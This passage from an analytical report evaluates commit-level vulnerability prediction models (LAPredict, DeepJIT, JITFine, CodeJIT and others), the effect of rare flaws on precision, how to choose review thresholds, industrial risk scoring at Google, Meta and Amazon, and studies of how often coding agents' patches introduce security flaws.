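Ranking changes by this score was a poor way to use limited review time. If reviewers could read only 20% of all modified lines and started with the highest-scoring changes, they would have found 5% of the buggy changes in the open-source projects and 8% in the commercial ones, compared with the 20% expected from reading in random order. The highest-scoring changes were so long that reviewers would run out of time after a few of them. A second model, which predicted bugs per modified line, raised the figures to 28% and 43%.

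LAPredict, which Zhengran Zeng and colleagues published in 2021, scores a commit using logistic regression on a single input, the number of lines added. They found that it could match much more complex models at predicting ordinary bugs, which suggested that those models had learned little more than that large changes are risky.

Tree ensembles use the same measurements as logistic regression but combine them differently. A decision tree applies a series of tests, such as whether the change adds more than 200 lines and, if so, whether the author has made fewer than ten changes before. A random forest trains many trees on different random samples of the data and combines their outputs into a score. Trees can therefore learn that large changes are risky mainly when the author is new, whereas the regression above adds the same amount for size whoever the author is. TLEL, from 2017, combines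 several random forests in two layers. When Nguyen and colleagues tested these models on known vulnerabilities in FFmpeg and Linux, TLEL ranked commits slightly better than logistic regression on the 14 measures, and LAPredict ranked them worse. Size alone seems to be a weaker guide to vulnerabilities than to bugs in general.

### Models that take in the code itself

DeepJIT, from 2019, takes the commit message and the changed lines of code as input instead of hand-made measurements. It converts each word or symbol into a list of numbers, then passes the message and the code through separate convolutional neural networks, which detect informative patterns in short runs of neighbouring words. Each network summarises its text as one list of numbers, and a final layer joins the two lists and computes the score. Training adjusts the numbers for each word or symbol, both networks and the final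 layer together to fit the labels.

One drawback of DeepJIT is that it has to learn what words and symbols mean from a few thousand labelled commits. JITFine, from 2022, instead starts from CodeBERT, a language model with 125 million parameters already trained on a large collection of code and English. CodeBERT turns the message and the changed code into a list of numbers, and another network combines this list with the 14 measures of Kamei and colleagues to produce the score. SimCom combines the same information more crudely, by training a tree model on the 14 measures and a neural network on the text, then averaging their scores.

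Commit messages can mislead these models. The CodeJIT paper describes an FFmpeg commit that reset an invalid value to 2, which prevented one out-of-bounds read but caused another serious problem. The commit added only two lines, and its message contained the word "Fixes". LAPredict and the models that use messages all classified it as safe.

CodeJIT, from 2023, uses graphs of the code rather than messages, authors or line counts. It builds one graph of the code before the change and another of the code after it. The nodes are pieces of code, from whole statements down to single symbols. "Structure" edges connect a statement to its parts, and "dependency" edges connect two statements when one affects the other, for instance by setting a variable that the other uses. CodeJIT then merges the two graphs, marks every node and edge as added, deleted or unchanged, and discards the parts unrelated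 to the change.

In the buffer example, the merged graph would contain the old limit, marked as deleted, and the new one, marked as added. Dependency edges would link the comparison to the two unchanged lines that measure the name and copy it. The graph would therefore contain all the information needed to recognise the overflow, none of which appears in a count of added lines.

A graph neural network then processes the result. Each node starts with a list of numbers that represents its content and its mark. In each round, the network combines every node's numbers with those of its neighbours, so after two rounds each node also carries information from its neighbours' neighbours. In the team's tests, using two rounds instead of one raised precision by 67% and lowered recall by 7%. The model then pools all the nodes into one list of numbers, which a small network uses to classify the commit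 as dangerous or not.

When Nguyen and colleagues tested CodeJIT on commits later than the training data, it reached 78% precision and 70% recall for known vulnerabilities, compared with 62% and 73% for JITFine. These figures are much higher than a working screen would achieve, because every commit in the test had either introduced or fixed a vulnerability. Building the graphs is also slow. The team could run CodeJIT on FFmpeg but not on Linux, which would have required too much computation.

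### What has followed since 2025

All of these models are at least three years old, and research has since moved in several directions, including making them easier to use and compare. *VulGuard* (Nguyen, Tran-Duc and colleagues, 2025) packages eight of them in a single program that extracts the measurements from a Git repository, trains the models and scores new commits. With 50 parallel processes, extraction took about an hour for FFmpeg and 12 hours for Linux.

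The knowledge-graph predictor by Hesamolhokama and colleagues tries to supply information about the rest of the project, which earlier models lacked. It keeps a permanent graph of the repository's history, the structure of its files and the meaning of its commits. When a commit arrives, the predictor updates only the affected part of the graph, recording which pieces of code the commit added, removed, altered or moved. In tests on ordinary bugs in 11 Apache projects, the average of its F1 scores for buggy and clean commits was higher than that of logistic regression and DeepJIT on all 11 projects, and higher than that of LAPredict on ten.

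*Deployment Risk Assessment Using Diff-Aware Features* (2026), a case study at Amazon's Prime Video, uses a large language model only to read the diff and fill in a set of structured measurements. A small conventional classifier then turns these into a risk estimate. This design lets the system handle many programming languages without a separate analyser for each, and the scoring step takes little compute and is fairly easy to inspect.

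Other systems prompt a language model to review the change and describe possible flaws rather than estimate a risk score.

### Whether the models notice which way a change goes

A model that takes in the diff may not use the information it contains about what the change does. Nam and colleagues designed an experiment to find out. Their dataset, ReDef, contains 3,164 defective and 10,268 clean changes from 22 C and C++ projects, each confined to a single function. The defective changes contain ordinary bugs, and developers later reverted them, usually with an explanation. Two of the researchers checked 100 of these defective changes by hand and judged 92 to be correctly labelled.

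The researchers trained four language models to classify the changes: CodeBERT, CodeT5+, UniXcoder and the largest, Qwen2.5, which had 7 billion parameters. They presented each change in five ways and tested the models on later changes than those in the training data. The table gives F1 scores averaged over ten runs, with inputs limited to about 512 tokens.

| What the model receives | CodeBERT | CodeT5+ | UniXcoder | Qwen2.5 |
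|---|---|---|---|---|
| The new function only | 0.373 | 0.363 | 0.350 | 0.339 |
| The new function, with changed lines marked | 0.352 | 0.338 | 0.321 | 0.342 |
| The old function, then the new one | 0.352 | 0.312 | 0.320 | 0.338 |
| A diff with lines tagged as added or deleted | 0.395 | 0.376 | 0.376 | 0.354 |
| A block of added lines, then a block of deleted lines | 0.397 | 0.377 | 0.372 | 0.350 |

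The two compact formats did best, partly because many whole functions exceeded the models' input limit and were cut off at the end, sometimes losing the edit itself. Doubling the limit did not help. UniXcoder's score on tagged diffs fell from 0.376 to 0.340, so the extra unchanged code may also have hurt performance.

None of these scores is good. About 24% of the changes were defective, and flagging every change would have given an F1 score of 0.38. Nam and colleagues describe their models as substantially better than random, which seems overstated. CodeBERT learned something, since its precision in its best format was 31%, compared with 24% for random flagging. Qwen2.5's precision was at most 26%.

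The researchers then corrupted the information about the change by swapping the added and deleted lines. If a fix replaces `use(p);` with `if (p) use(p);`, so that the program checks that `p` exists before using it, the swapped version removes that check. A model that had learned the difference between a repair and a new fault should do much worse on swapped data.

| Corruption | CodeBERT: before → after | Qwen2.5: before → after |
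|---|---|---|
| Change markers placed at random | 0.352 → 0.353 | 0.342 → 0.333 |
| Old and new functions swapped half the time | 0.352 → 0.354 | 0.338 → 0.339 |
| "Added" and "deleted" tags reversed | 0.395 → 0.392 | 0.354 → 0.341 |
| Added and deleted blocks swapped half the time | 0.397 → 0.395 | 0.350 → 0.350 |

The random markers and swapped blocks were in both the training and test data, so those rows show that models trained without reliable information about the change did just as well. In the other two rows, the models were trained on correct data and only the test data was corrupted.

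Nam and colleagues conclude that the models relied on surface cues, such as which words appear in the code, with no real understanding of the change. The evidence for this is convincing for CodeBERT but more mixed for Qwen2.5. CodeBERT scored roughly 0.06 above the 0.33 or so expected from random flagging with the same recall, and it kept nearly all of that lead when the tags were reversed. Qwen2.5's lead over random flagging on tagged diffs was only about 0.02, and reversing the tags removed more than half of it. Qwen2.5 may have made some use of the direction of the change, but it was so inaccurate to begin with that the drop looks negligible.

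Surface cues can still help a screen. Code full of pointers and manual memory handling is probably riskier to edit than code that prints a message, and a model can learn this without working out what any particular edit does. But such a model would give about the same score to a commit that adds a safety check as to one that removes it.

The experiment left out commit messages, commit authors and the rest of the project, each of which some predictors use. It also tested only models that are small by current standards. CodeBERT, the smallest of the four, did best, but this is little evidence of how models far larger than Qwen2.5 would do. Nam and colleagues left those models for future work.

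## Accuracy when flawed commits are rare, and the choice of threshold

Most early tests of vulnerability predictors used only commits that had introduced or fixed a known vulnerability, but a screen in daily use mostly receives commits that did neither. In 2025, Nguyen and colleagues measured the effect of this difference by testing eight predictors on 88,178 commits from FFmpeg and 993,704 from the Linux kernel.

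### The same models in two settings

The researchers collected the commits on each project's main branch up to 24 September 2024, leaving out merges, edits to whitespace or comments, and commits that changed no C or C++ code. They split the history by date, using the oldest stretch, with 75% of the VICs, for training, the next 5% for tuning and the newest 20% for testing. Every model was therefore tested on commits later than those in its training data, as it would be in use.

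In the idealised setting, the data contained only VICs and the commits that fixed vulnerabilities (VFCs). The realistic setting added all the other commits.

Two measures, PR-AUC and ROC-AUC, help to compare the settings. Lowering the threshold raises recall and usually lowers precision, and plotting precision against recall gives a precision-recall curve. PR-AUC is the area under this curve, which is roughly the average precision over all levels of recall. A perfect ranking scores 1, while a random ranking scores about the base rate, because at any threshold the flagged commits are no more likely to be flawed than the rest. ROC-AUC is the probability that a randomly chosen flawed commit scores higher than a randomly chosen harmless one. A random ranking gets 0.5, however rare flaws are.

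The table gives the idealised result first and the realistic one second. All the results concern known vulnerabilities, presumably almost all accidental.

| Model | FFmpeg PR-AUC | FFmpeg ROC-AUC | Linux PR-AUC | Linux ROC-AUC |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| VCCFinder | 0.895 → 0.071 | 0.948 → 0.688 | 0.809 → 0.013 | 0.867 → 0.588 |
| LAPredict | 0.558 → 0.041 | 0.620 → 0.591 | 0.610 → 0.010 | 0.699 → 0.591 |
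| Logistic regression | 0.780 → 0.093 | 0.865 → 0.769 | 0.788 → 0.023 | 0.825 → 0.746 |
| TLEL | 0.850 → 0.112 | 0.918 → 0.795 | 0.829 → 0.027 | 0.881 → 0.787 |
| SimCom | 0.921 → 0.134 | 0.954 → 0.809 | 0.892 → 0.031 | 0.913 → 0.779 |
| DeepJIT | 0.906 → 0.082 | 0.946 → 0.746 | 0.823 → 0.005 | 0.873 → 0.497 |
| JITFine | 0.959 → 0.111 | 0.980 → 0.790 | 0.885 → 0.005 | 0.915 → 0.497 |
| CodeJIT | 0.798 → 0.079 | 0.838 → 0.721 | not run | not run |
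| Average | 0.833 → 0.091 | 0.884 → 0.738 | 0.805 → 0.016 | 0.853 → 0.641 |
| Random ranking | 0.35 → 0.025 | 0.5 → 0.5 | 0.35 → 0.006 | 0.5 → 0.5 |

Training on all commits made little difference. Models trained only on VICs and VFCs averaged 0.076 on the realistic FFmpeg test and 0.017 on the Linux one.

The last row of the table is calculated from the paper's counts, because the paper's text is inconsistent about how rare VICs are. It gives one VIC for every 217 safe Linux commits in one place and one for every 127 in another. The Linux test set has 922 VICs among 157,961 commits, which is 0.58%, or one for every 170 safe commits. The FFmpeg test set has 1,020 among 40,701, which is 2.5%, or one for every 39 safe commits. The text gives a much higher rate for FFmpeg, one in 17, which roughly matches the project's whole history. In FFmpeg's training data, 8.8% of commits were VICs. The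 newer commits in the test set may be safer, or people may not have found all their flaws yet.

### How much of the fall is arithmetic

We can learn almost nothing about the models from the 98% fall in average PR-AUC on Linux that Nguyen and colleagues emphasise, because a random ranking's PR-AUC would also have fallen by 98%. A random ranking scores about the same as the share of VICs in the test set, which was 35% in the idealised Linux set and 0.58% in the realistic one. The same problem applies to FFmpeg, where the random ranking's score fell by 93% and the models' by 89%.

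A model's score relative to the floor is more informative. In the realistic setting, the models averaged 3.6 times the floor on FFmpeg and 2.7 times on Linux. SimCom, the best, scored just over five times the floor on both. DeepJIT and JITFine did no better than chance on Linux, although they were among the strongest models in the idealised setting.

Some of the loss is real, however, because ROC-AUC also fell and rarity alone cannot lower it. The models evidently find it harder to tell a VIC from an ordinary commit than from a fix, probably because fixes are easy to recognise from their messages, which often mention what they repair. The models' earlier scores may therefore have come partly from recognising fixes rather than vulnerabilities. On FFmpeg, ROC-AUC fell by an average of 0.20 for the four models that use commit messages and 0.09 for the other four.

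Nguyen and colleagues consider ROC-AUC less suitable for such unbalanced data. It can make a screen look better than it is. On Linux, for example, TLEL had a ROC-AUC of 0.787 but a PR-AUC of 0.027. ROC-AUC is still the better guide to whether a model has learned anything, although PR-AUC better reflects what its users would experience.

### From rates to alerts

Suppose that a screen has 80% recall and a false-alarm rate of 10%, meaning that it flags a tenth of the harmless commits. Its precision depends on the test set:

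| Test set | Flawed | Harmless | True alarms | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linux, VICs and VFCs only | 922 | 1,691 | 738 | 169 | 81% |
| FFmpeg, all commits | 1,020 | 39,681 | 816 | 3,968 | 17% |
| Linux, all commits | 922 | 157,039 | 738 | 15,704 | 4.5% |

On the full Linux set, reviewers would read about 22 flagged commits for each flaw they found, compared with 171 if they chose commits at random. The screen would miss 184 flaws. The false-alarm rate would have to fall from 10% to 0.47% for half of the alarms to be real at the same recall.

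These assumed rates are generous. A model with 80% recall and a 10% false-alarm rate would normally have a ROC-AUC of at least 0.85, and none of the eight models reached that in the realistic setting.

Some newer work still uses nearly balanced data. *Detecting Vulnerability-Inducing Commits via Multi-Stage Reasoning with LLM-Based Agents* (Chen, Sun and colleagues, 2026) tests a system in which language-model agents summarise a commit and its purpose, list suspected flaws and then re-examine each one. With the DeepSeek-V3.2 model, the system flagged 51 of 106 VICs and 22 of 135 VFCs, for a precision of 70%. At the same rates on the Linux test set, it would raise about 444 true alarms and 25,600 false ones, a precision of 1.7%. Real precision could be higher, because ordinary commits may trigger fewer false alarms than security fixes do, but Chen and colleagues tested no ordinary commits.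 They also removed false alarms from the system's store of past cases by checking them against the true labels, which nobody would have when a new commit arrives.

### Rebalancing the training data

When flawed commits are rare, a model can fit its training data quite well by labeling every commit safe. Nguyen and colleagues tried five standard remedies, applied only to the training data. The table shows the PR-AUC for each remedy, averaged over the models they applied it to.

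| Remedy | How it works | Project and models | PR-AUC before → after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random undersampling | Discards safe commits until the classes are equal | FFmpeg, seven | 0.092 → 0.114 |
| Random undersampling | As above | Linux, seven | 0.016 → 0.062 |
| Random oversampling | Duplicates VICs until the classes are equal | FFmpeg, seven | 0.092 → 0.084 |
| SMOTE | Creates artificial VICs by blending the measurements of real ones | FFmpeg, three | 0.082 → 0.084 |
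| One-sided selection | Discards safe commits that seem redundant or noisy | FFmpeg, three | 0.082 → 0.080 |
| Focal loss | Gives more weight to examples the model gets wrong | FFmpeg, SimCom | 0.134 → 0.110 |
| Focal loss | As above | FFmpeg, DeepJIT | 0.082 → 0.018 |

Focal loss changes the penalty that training tries to minimise. If *p* is the probability that the model gives to the correct label, the example contributes

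−*α*(1 − *p*)^*γ* log *p*

where *α* is a weight for the class, and *γ* was 2 in these tests. An example with *p* = 0.9 has its usual penalty multiplied by 0.01, and one with *p* = 0.5 by 0.25. This should stop thousands of easy, safe commits from swamping the few VICs. In practice both models ended with F1 scores of zero, and DeepJIT ranked commits worse than chance.

Nguyen and colleagues conclude that the remedies are ineffective. That conclusion is fair for four of the remedies, but undersampling had a large effect on some Linux models. It raised DeepJIT from 0.005 to 0.160, JITFine from 0.005 to 0.122 and VCCFinder from 0.013 to 0.067. Logistic regression stayed at 0.023, probably because rebalancing mostly raised all its scores together without changing their order.

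DeepJIT ranked Linux commits better after undersampling, but its F1 score was 0.012, which is what a screen that flagged every commit would get. The threshold for flagging a commit no longer suited the model's scores.

The gain also may not carry over to other data. Tran and colleagues trained all six of their models, including DeepJIT and JITFine, with undersampling. Average PR-AUC on Linux was only about 0.004 to 0.006, so none of them can have reached 0.160. Their Linux data covered two years rather than the whole history, so the models may have had too few VICs to learn from.

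### Ranking under a review budget

PR-AUC covers every possible threshold, including many that no team would use. Effort-aware measures start from the time reviewers have. The VulGuard program by Nguyen and colleagues reports three of them:

- Recall@20 is the share of flaws found in the top 20% of the ranking.
- Effort@20 is the share of the code that reviewers must read to find 20% of the flaws.
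- P-opt compares the model's order with the best possible one.

Ranking by risk per line can help reviewers reach more flaws in the same time, but it has a drawback. In the invented example below, six changes contain 1,000 lines in total, and reviewers have time to read 200.

| Change | Lines | Score | Score per 100 lines | Flawed? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | 500 | 0.9 | 0.18 | yes |
| B | 250 | 0.8 | 0.32 | no |
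| C | 100 | 0.6 | 0.60 | yes |
| D | 60 | 0.3 | 0.50 | no |
| E | 50 | 0.1 | 0.20 | no |
| F | 40 | 0.4 | 1.00 | yes |

Ranking by score per line puts F, C and D first. The reviewers finish all three within 200 lines and find two of the three flaws, reaching the first after 4% of the code. But they never open A, which has the highest score. A project that always ranked changes this way would rarely review its largest ones.

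The prioritization test by Tran and colleagues used five review budgets, counted in commits rather than lines. With the best training labels, the models found 39% of the VICs on average. Random selection would have found 11.5%, the average of the five budgets. The same models' PR-AUC averaged only 0.022. The two results are consistent because reviewers who follow such a ranking find over three times as many flaws in the same number of commits, but nearly every commit they read is still harmless.

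The researchers chose each threshold from the scores of the test commits. A live screen has to set its threshold from past scores, so the number of flagged changes will vary from week to week.

### Choosing the threshold

The simplest way to choose a threshold is to base it on review capacity. If a team receives 2,000 changes a week and can examine 100 closely, it can set the threshold at the 95th percentile of recent scores, so that about 5% of new changes exceed it. If coding agents then double the number of changes while the number of reviewers stays the same, the team has to raise the threshold to the 97.5th percentile, and recall will fall.

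A second method starts from costs. Let *p* be the probability that a change is flawed, *q* the chance that a close review catches the flaw, *M* the cost of missing it and *R* the cost of the review. The review is worthwhile when

*p* × *q* × *M* > *R*, or *p* > *R* / (*qM*)

Suppose a close review costs $100 and catches half of all flaws, and a missed flaw costs $10,000. The team should then review any change with more than a 2% chance of being flawed. If a missed flaw costs $50,000, the threshold falls to 0.4%. That is below the Linux base rate, so even an average commit would be worth reviewing, and the screen would only be useful for identifying the safest commits, which could skip review. By this calculation, a team that can't afford that many reviews has too few reviewers.

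The rule applies to the lowest-scoring flagged change, which is riskier than the changes below the threshold but safer than the average flagged change. A screen can therefore have acceptable overall precision even when its lowest-scoring alarms waste reviewers' time.

The rule also needs real probabilities, so a team has to correct the inflated scores of a model trained on balanced data. If the score *s* is accurate for such data and the true base rate is *b*, the corrected odds are

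*p* / (1 − *p*) = *s* / (1 − *s*) × *b* / (1 − *b*)

At the Linux base rate, a score of 0.5 corresponds to a 0.58% chance of a flaw, and a score of 0.9 to about 5%. The 2% cut-off falls at a score of about 0.78. The common default threshold of 0.5 has no special meaning here. If agent patches have a different base rate from human ones, the same score will correspond to a different risk for each.

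### Directing review and blocking merges

Closely reviewing a harmless commit takes some of a reviewer's time, but automatically rejecting every flagged commit would be much worse. With the assumed rates of 80% and 10%, that rule would reject 16,442 Linux commits, of which 15,704 were harmless. Their authors would often have nothing specific to correct.

Wrongly blocking a commit has a larger *R* in the cost rule, so blocking requires a higher *p*. On Linux, none of the eight models came close to the precision needed for blocking, except perhaps on a handful of top-ranked commits. A security reviewer could still use their rankings to choose which commits to read first.

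Letting low-scoring commits skip human review also risks missing flaws. In the same example, 184 of the 141,519 unflagged commits would be flawed. That rate, 0.13%, is less than a quarter of the base rate, but those 184 commits are a fifth of all the flawed ones. Whether this is acceptable depends on what other checks the unflagged commits have to pass.

### Risk scores at Google, Meta and Amazon

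The best published figures for a vulnerability screen come from Google. *Predicting Likely-Vulnerable Code Changes* (Yim, 2024) tested a random forest on about six years of changes to Android's media code, retraining it every month. The model caught about 80% of the changes that introduced known vulnerabilities, with 98% precision and about seven false alarms a month.

This test was easier than the Linux one for two reasons. Vulnerabilities were common, at 7.4% of changes, because Google had tested this code unusually heavily and found many flaws. More importantly, the test assumed that everyone knew about a flaw as soon as the change that introduced it was merged. Yim acknowledges that it would be more realistic to treat a flaw as known only once it was fixed. In the Linux data described earlier, developers fixed less than 3% of vulnerabilities within a month. The assumption matters because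 the model used records of where vulnerabilities had recently appeared. In a separate test on shuffled data from the first year, recall was 60% with all features, but 32% without those records and the histories of individual engineers. The 80% figure is therefore best read as what the screen might do if other testing found flaws almost immediately.

Meta has used a risk score in production, but to predict severe incidents that affect users, such as outages or serious privacy and security problems. In *Moving Faster and Reducing Risk*, Abreu, Murali and colleagues (2024) tested it on 181,052 changes, of which 305 (0.17%) had caused such incidents. The table shows how many of these incidents Meta would have caught by holding back the riskiest changes. The language model has 13 billion parameters, and Meta had trained it on its own past changes and incidents.

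| Changes held back | Incidents caught: logistic regression | Incidents caught: language model | Changes held per incident caught (language model) |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 18.7% | 26.2% | 113 |
| 10% | 27.9% | 42.3% | 140 |
| 50% | 84.6% | 88.5% | 335 |

Precision was below 1% at every threshold, yet Meta does block changes based on such a score. It can do so because the blocks are temporary and apply during code freezes, short periods when the company limits changes to its systems. A developer can wait for the freeze to end, revise the change or ask a manager for an exception. Meta also sets the threshold according to how much harm a missed risky change could do. It blocks 5% of changes at weekends, when fewer engineers are available to handle an incident, and 50% at times such as Black Friday, when an outage would affect the most users. Abreu and colleagues calculated these results from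 past data and did not measure how many incidents the blocks prevented.

Labels are more reliable in this setting than in most vulnerability research, because Meta's engineers investigate each incident and identify the change that triggered it. For *Deployment Risk Assessment Using Diff-Aware Features*, Amazon's Prime Video also had experts check by hand which commits had caused outages, and the researchers kept the natural ratio of 149 risky commits to 2,831 others.

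Meta now also uses its risk score to decide which changes need no human reviewer. *Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (Adams, Banga and colleagues, 2026) describes a system called RADAR that had reviewed 535,000 changes and merged 331,000 of them. By default, a person's change must be among the safest 5% by risk score to qualify. For AI agents and other bots, the limit is the safest 20%, or 50% for approved types of task, many of them routine, such as removing unused code. Each type of agent task must also have gone 60 days without causing a production incident. In addition to scoring low enough, these changes must pass fixed rules and a language-model reviewer, which sends a change to a human if it finds any sign of risk, including a security flaw.

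Changes that went through RADAR caused production incidents at one fiftieth of the rate of other changes, and developers reverted them a third as often. Adams and colleagues note that this does not show cause and effect, since RADAR accepts only changes that already look safe. The score alone probably cannot explain so large a gap, because in the 2024 test the lower-scoring half of changes still caused 35 of the 305 incidents, about an eighth as many as the other half. The other checks and the simplicity of the tasks presumably account for much of the rest. A low incident rate also does not mean that few vulnerabilities got through. An outage usually becomes obvious soon after a change goes live, but a vulnerability can remain unnoticed for years without causing an incident.

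## Accidental flaws in patches written by coding agents

A screen's precision depends on how often the changes it receives are flawed, so a project screening agent patches needs an estimate of that rate. Published estimates range from about 0.1% to 87%. The studies behind them cover different agents and tasks, count different things as flaws, and rarely measure human code the same way for comparison. None of them looked for deliberate flaws, so their figures presumably describe accidental ones.

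### Models and developers on the same issues

Sajadi, Damevski and Chatterjee (2025), in *Are AI-Generated Fixes Secure?*, compared people and models on the same tasks. They used SWE-bench, a collection of real issues (bug reports and feature requests) from popular Python projects, each paired with the change that developers merged to resolve it. They had the language model Llama 3.3 write its own solutions to 21,294 issues. The model had no agent tools. It received each issue and the files the developers had changed, and returned complete new versions of those files.

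Three static analysers scanned the files before and after each change. The researchers counted a new vulnerability only if at least two analysers reported it in the same file.

| Patches by | Semgrep | CodeQL | Bandit | Files where at least two agree |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 | 323 | 62 | 1,055 | 185 |
| Developers | 9 | 41 | 1,348 | 17 |

Llama introduced a vulnerability in at most 0.9% of issues under the two-analyser rule, and developers did so in at most 0.08%. But the gap depends heavily on the analyser. Llama had 36 times as many Semgrep findings as the developers, while Bandit alone would make the developers look worse.

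For 2,294 of the issues, the researchers also scanned published patches by three agents: OpenHands and AutoCodeRover, both running on Claude 3.5 Sonnet, and Honeycomb. Excluding test files and scripts that only reproduced a bug, they counted 148 vulnerabilities from OpenHands, three from AutoCodeRover and two from Honeycomb. The 148 from OpenHands came from 15 issues, three of which accounted for 124. One OpenHands diff ran to more than 500,000 lines, which a simple size limit would have stopped. OpenHands introduced vulnerabilities in 0.7% of issues and the other two agents in about 0.1%, which is too few cases to distinguish from the developers' rate.

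The comparison also favours the developers, because their patches had passed review. Nobody had reviewed the agents' patches, and many did not work. OpenHands resolved only 29% of the issues. The models are also old by now.

Llama's most common flaws were command injection (97 cases), which lets an attacker run operating-system commands, and eval injection (54). In a patch for Qiskit, a quantum-computing library, Llama passed text from the user to Python's `eval()` function, which runs its input as code. The developers' code strictly checked such text first. They introduced few flaws, which included command injection but not eval injection.

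### Agents' pull requests on GitHub

Much of the evidence from real projects comes from AIDev, a public dataset of pull requests by five agents: OpenAI Codex, Devin, GitHub Copilot, Cursor and Claude Code. *The Quiet Contributions* (Hasan, Rabbi and Zibran, 2026) examines 4,762 of these pull requests to Python projects with more than 100 stars (users' bookmarks on GitHub). All were "silent", meaning they were merged or closed without comment or discussion. About 70% of the agents' pull requests to such projects were silent.

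The researchers ran Semgrep on each project before and after the change. In 98.53% of cases, the number of reported vulnerabilities stayed the same.

This is a net figure, so a pull request that removes one flaw and adds another counts as no change. Among Codex's merged pull requests, for example, 1.21% introduced a finding of type CWE-706 (a name that can lead to the wrong file or resource) and 1.10% removed one. Codex wrote 96% of the sample, so the result is weak evidence about the other agents, and the sample included no human pull requests for comparison.

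Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues (2026) found a much higher rate using the same dataset and analyser in *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests*. They used keywords and a language model to select 675 security-related pull requests in several programming languages. They then counted every Semgrep finding that was absent before the change, even if the change had fixed other problems. At least one new finding appeared in 104 pull requests (15.4%), and one had 109.

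Of the 853 findings, 36% were inefficient regular expressions, text-matching patterns that an attacker can make extremely slow with crafted input. Another 13% were command injection, and 10% were path traversal, the flaw in the picture website. Reviewers merged many of the flawed pull requests.

Studies also differ in what they count as "security-related". In *Security in the Age of AI Teammates*, Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues (2026) searched the same 33,596 pull requests with a different keyword filter, checked the results by hand, and found 1,293, nearly twice as many. Most often, the agents were adding tests, documentation, settings or better error handling rather than repairing a vulnerability. Reviewers took longer to review these pull requests than others and merged them less often.

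### Who edited the file before a bug fix

The largest comparison with human work covers bugs of all kinds, not just vulnerabilities. Khosravani and Mockus (2026), in *Detecting AI Coding Agents in Open Source*, searched more than 180 million repositories for traces of agents. For commits in which a person fixed a bug, they checked whether an agent had made the previous commit to the same file. They then divided the agent's share of those previous commits by its share of all commits in the project, so chance alone would produce a ratio of 1. If an agent made 30% of a project's commits but only 10% of those just before a human fix, the ratio would be 0.33.

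| Agent | Ratio | Agent commits later reverted | Human commits later reverted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 0.33 | 1.1% | 1.6% |
| OpenHands | 0.38 | 1.38% | 1.03% |
| Aider | 0.56 | 0.17% | 0.90% |

Khosravani and Mockus take the low ratios as evidence that agents don't introduce more defects than people. The evidence is fairly weak. The ratios leave out bugs that agents fixed, and people may well ask an agent to repair its own mistakes. In the projects studied, 55% of Claude Code's commits had messages with bug-fix keywords. People also tend to return to files they have been working on, so a human fix would often follow a human commit even if the agent's code were just as buggy.

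The previous commit to a file may not have caused the bug, so the researchers compared attributing bugs to that commit with line-by-line SZZ on 357 cases. The two methods agreed on "human" or "AI" in 99% of them. But SZZ attributed only 1.1% of the cases to AI, so labeling every case "human" would have matched SZZ about as often.

The census and AIDev also cover largely different agents. Codex opened 814,522 pull requests in the full AIDev dataset, but the census found only 843 of its commits, because projects usually merge its work in a way that removes its name. Claude Code had 850,157 commits in the census but only 5,137 pull requests in AIDev. The low ratio for Claude Code is therefore no evidence about Codex, and the 98.53% figure is almost no evidence about Claude Code.

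### Tests with much higher rates

DryRun Security, a company that sells code-scanning software, had three agents each build a web app for tracking children's allergies and a multiplayer racing game. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents keep repeating decade-old security mistakes* names the agents as Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6, Codex with GPT-5.2, and Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. The prompts contained no security guidance. DryRun's own scanner found 143 issues, and 26 of the 30 pull requests (87%) had at least one.

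The finished applications looked somewhat better. Final scans of all six found 53 issues. The web app had nine issues before the agents started, and Codex's version ended with eight.

Endor Labs, another security company, describes a similarly poor result on SusVibes, a benchmark from Carnegie Mellon University. The best combination tested, SWE-Agent with Claude Sonnet 4, produced working code for 61% of tasks, but the code was also secure for only 10.5% of tasks, so more than 80% of the working solutions were vulnerable.

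1Password's *How information quality impacts LLMs' ability to patch complex, novel vulnerabilities* (2026) covers a different task, repairing known vulnerabilities. Claude Opus 4.8 and ChatGPT 5.5 attempted to fix six recently disclosed flaws in software including Linux and Chrome. 1Password analysed 6,080 patches after excluding attempts in which a model seemed to have looked up the official fix.

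| Result | Share of patches |
|---|---|
| Fixed the vulnerability cleanly | 26.0% |
| Fixed it but wrongly changed the program's behaviour | 20.1% |
| Left it unfixed, added a new vulnerability, or both | 53.9% |

The share of clean fixes rose to 31% when the prompt contained only correct information and fell to 15% when the prompt gave the wrong cause or remedy.

According to flyingpenguin's *Disinformation Pushed by 1Password*, a critical blog post, the paper reports that only 4.5% of patches introduced a new vulnerability. Nearly all the other failures in the 53.9% left the old flaw in place. Such a patch is dangerous if people believe it worked, but it is not a vulnerability-introducing commit.

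These figures come from *Frontier Models' Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, for which Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet deliberately chose flaws with complicated official fixes. Routine repairs would probably go better. The two models graded their own and each other's patches. According to the blog post, the paper acknowledges that this grading missed most of the defects it should have caught, so the true results may be worse. The study gives no human failure rate because it used the official fixes as the standard of correctness. A study of operating systems cited by Kamei and colleagues found that people's repairs go wrong too.

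### Why the rates differ so much

| Study | What the agents or models did | What counted | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sajadi and colleagues, three agents | Resolved issues in Python projects | New findings on which two analysers agreed | 0.1% to 0.7% of issues |
| Hasan and colleagues | Python pull requests that nobody discussed | A net change in Semgrep's count, up or down | 1.5% of pull requests |
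| 1Password | Repaired six complex vulnerabilities | New vulnerabilities, as judged by two models | 4.5% of patches |
| Rabbi and colleagues | Security-related pull requests | Any new Semgrep finding | 15.4% of pull requests |
| Endor Labs, on SusVibes | Benchmark programming tasks | Working code that was insecure | Over 80% of working solutions |
| DryRun Security | Built two applications | Any issue found by its own scanner | 87% of pull requests |

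Much of the spread comes from the choice of task. A pull request that adds user accounts to a new application offers many more chances for a security mistake than one that corrects a date format. DryRun's test was mostly the first kind of work. Its 87% may be a fair estimate for an agent that builds a new application without security instructions, but it would be a poor base rate for a mature project's daily pull requests.

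The measured flaw rate also depends on the detector. Requiring two static analysers to agree removes many false alarms but also discards real flaws that only one can find. Many of DryRun's findings were logic errors, which analysers based on text patterns generally miss. If DryRun's scanner was right about most of them, the rates from pattern-based analysers are too low.

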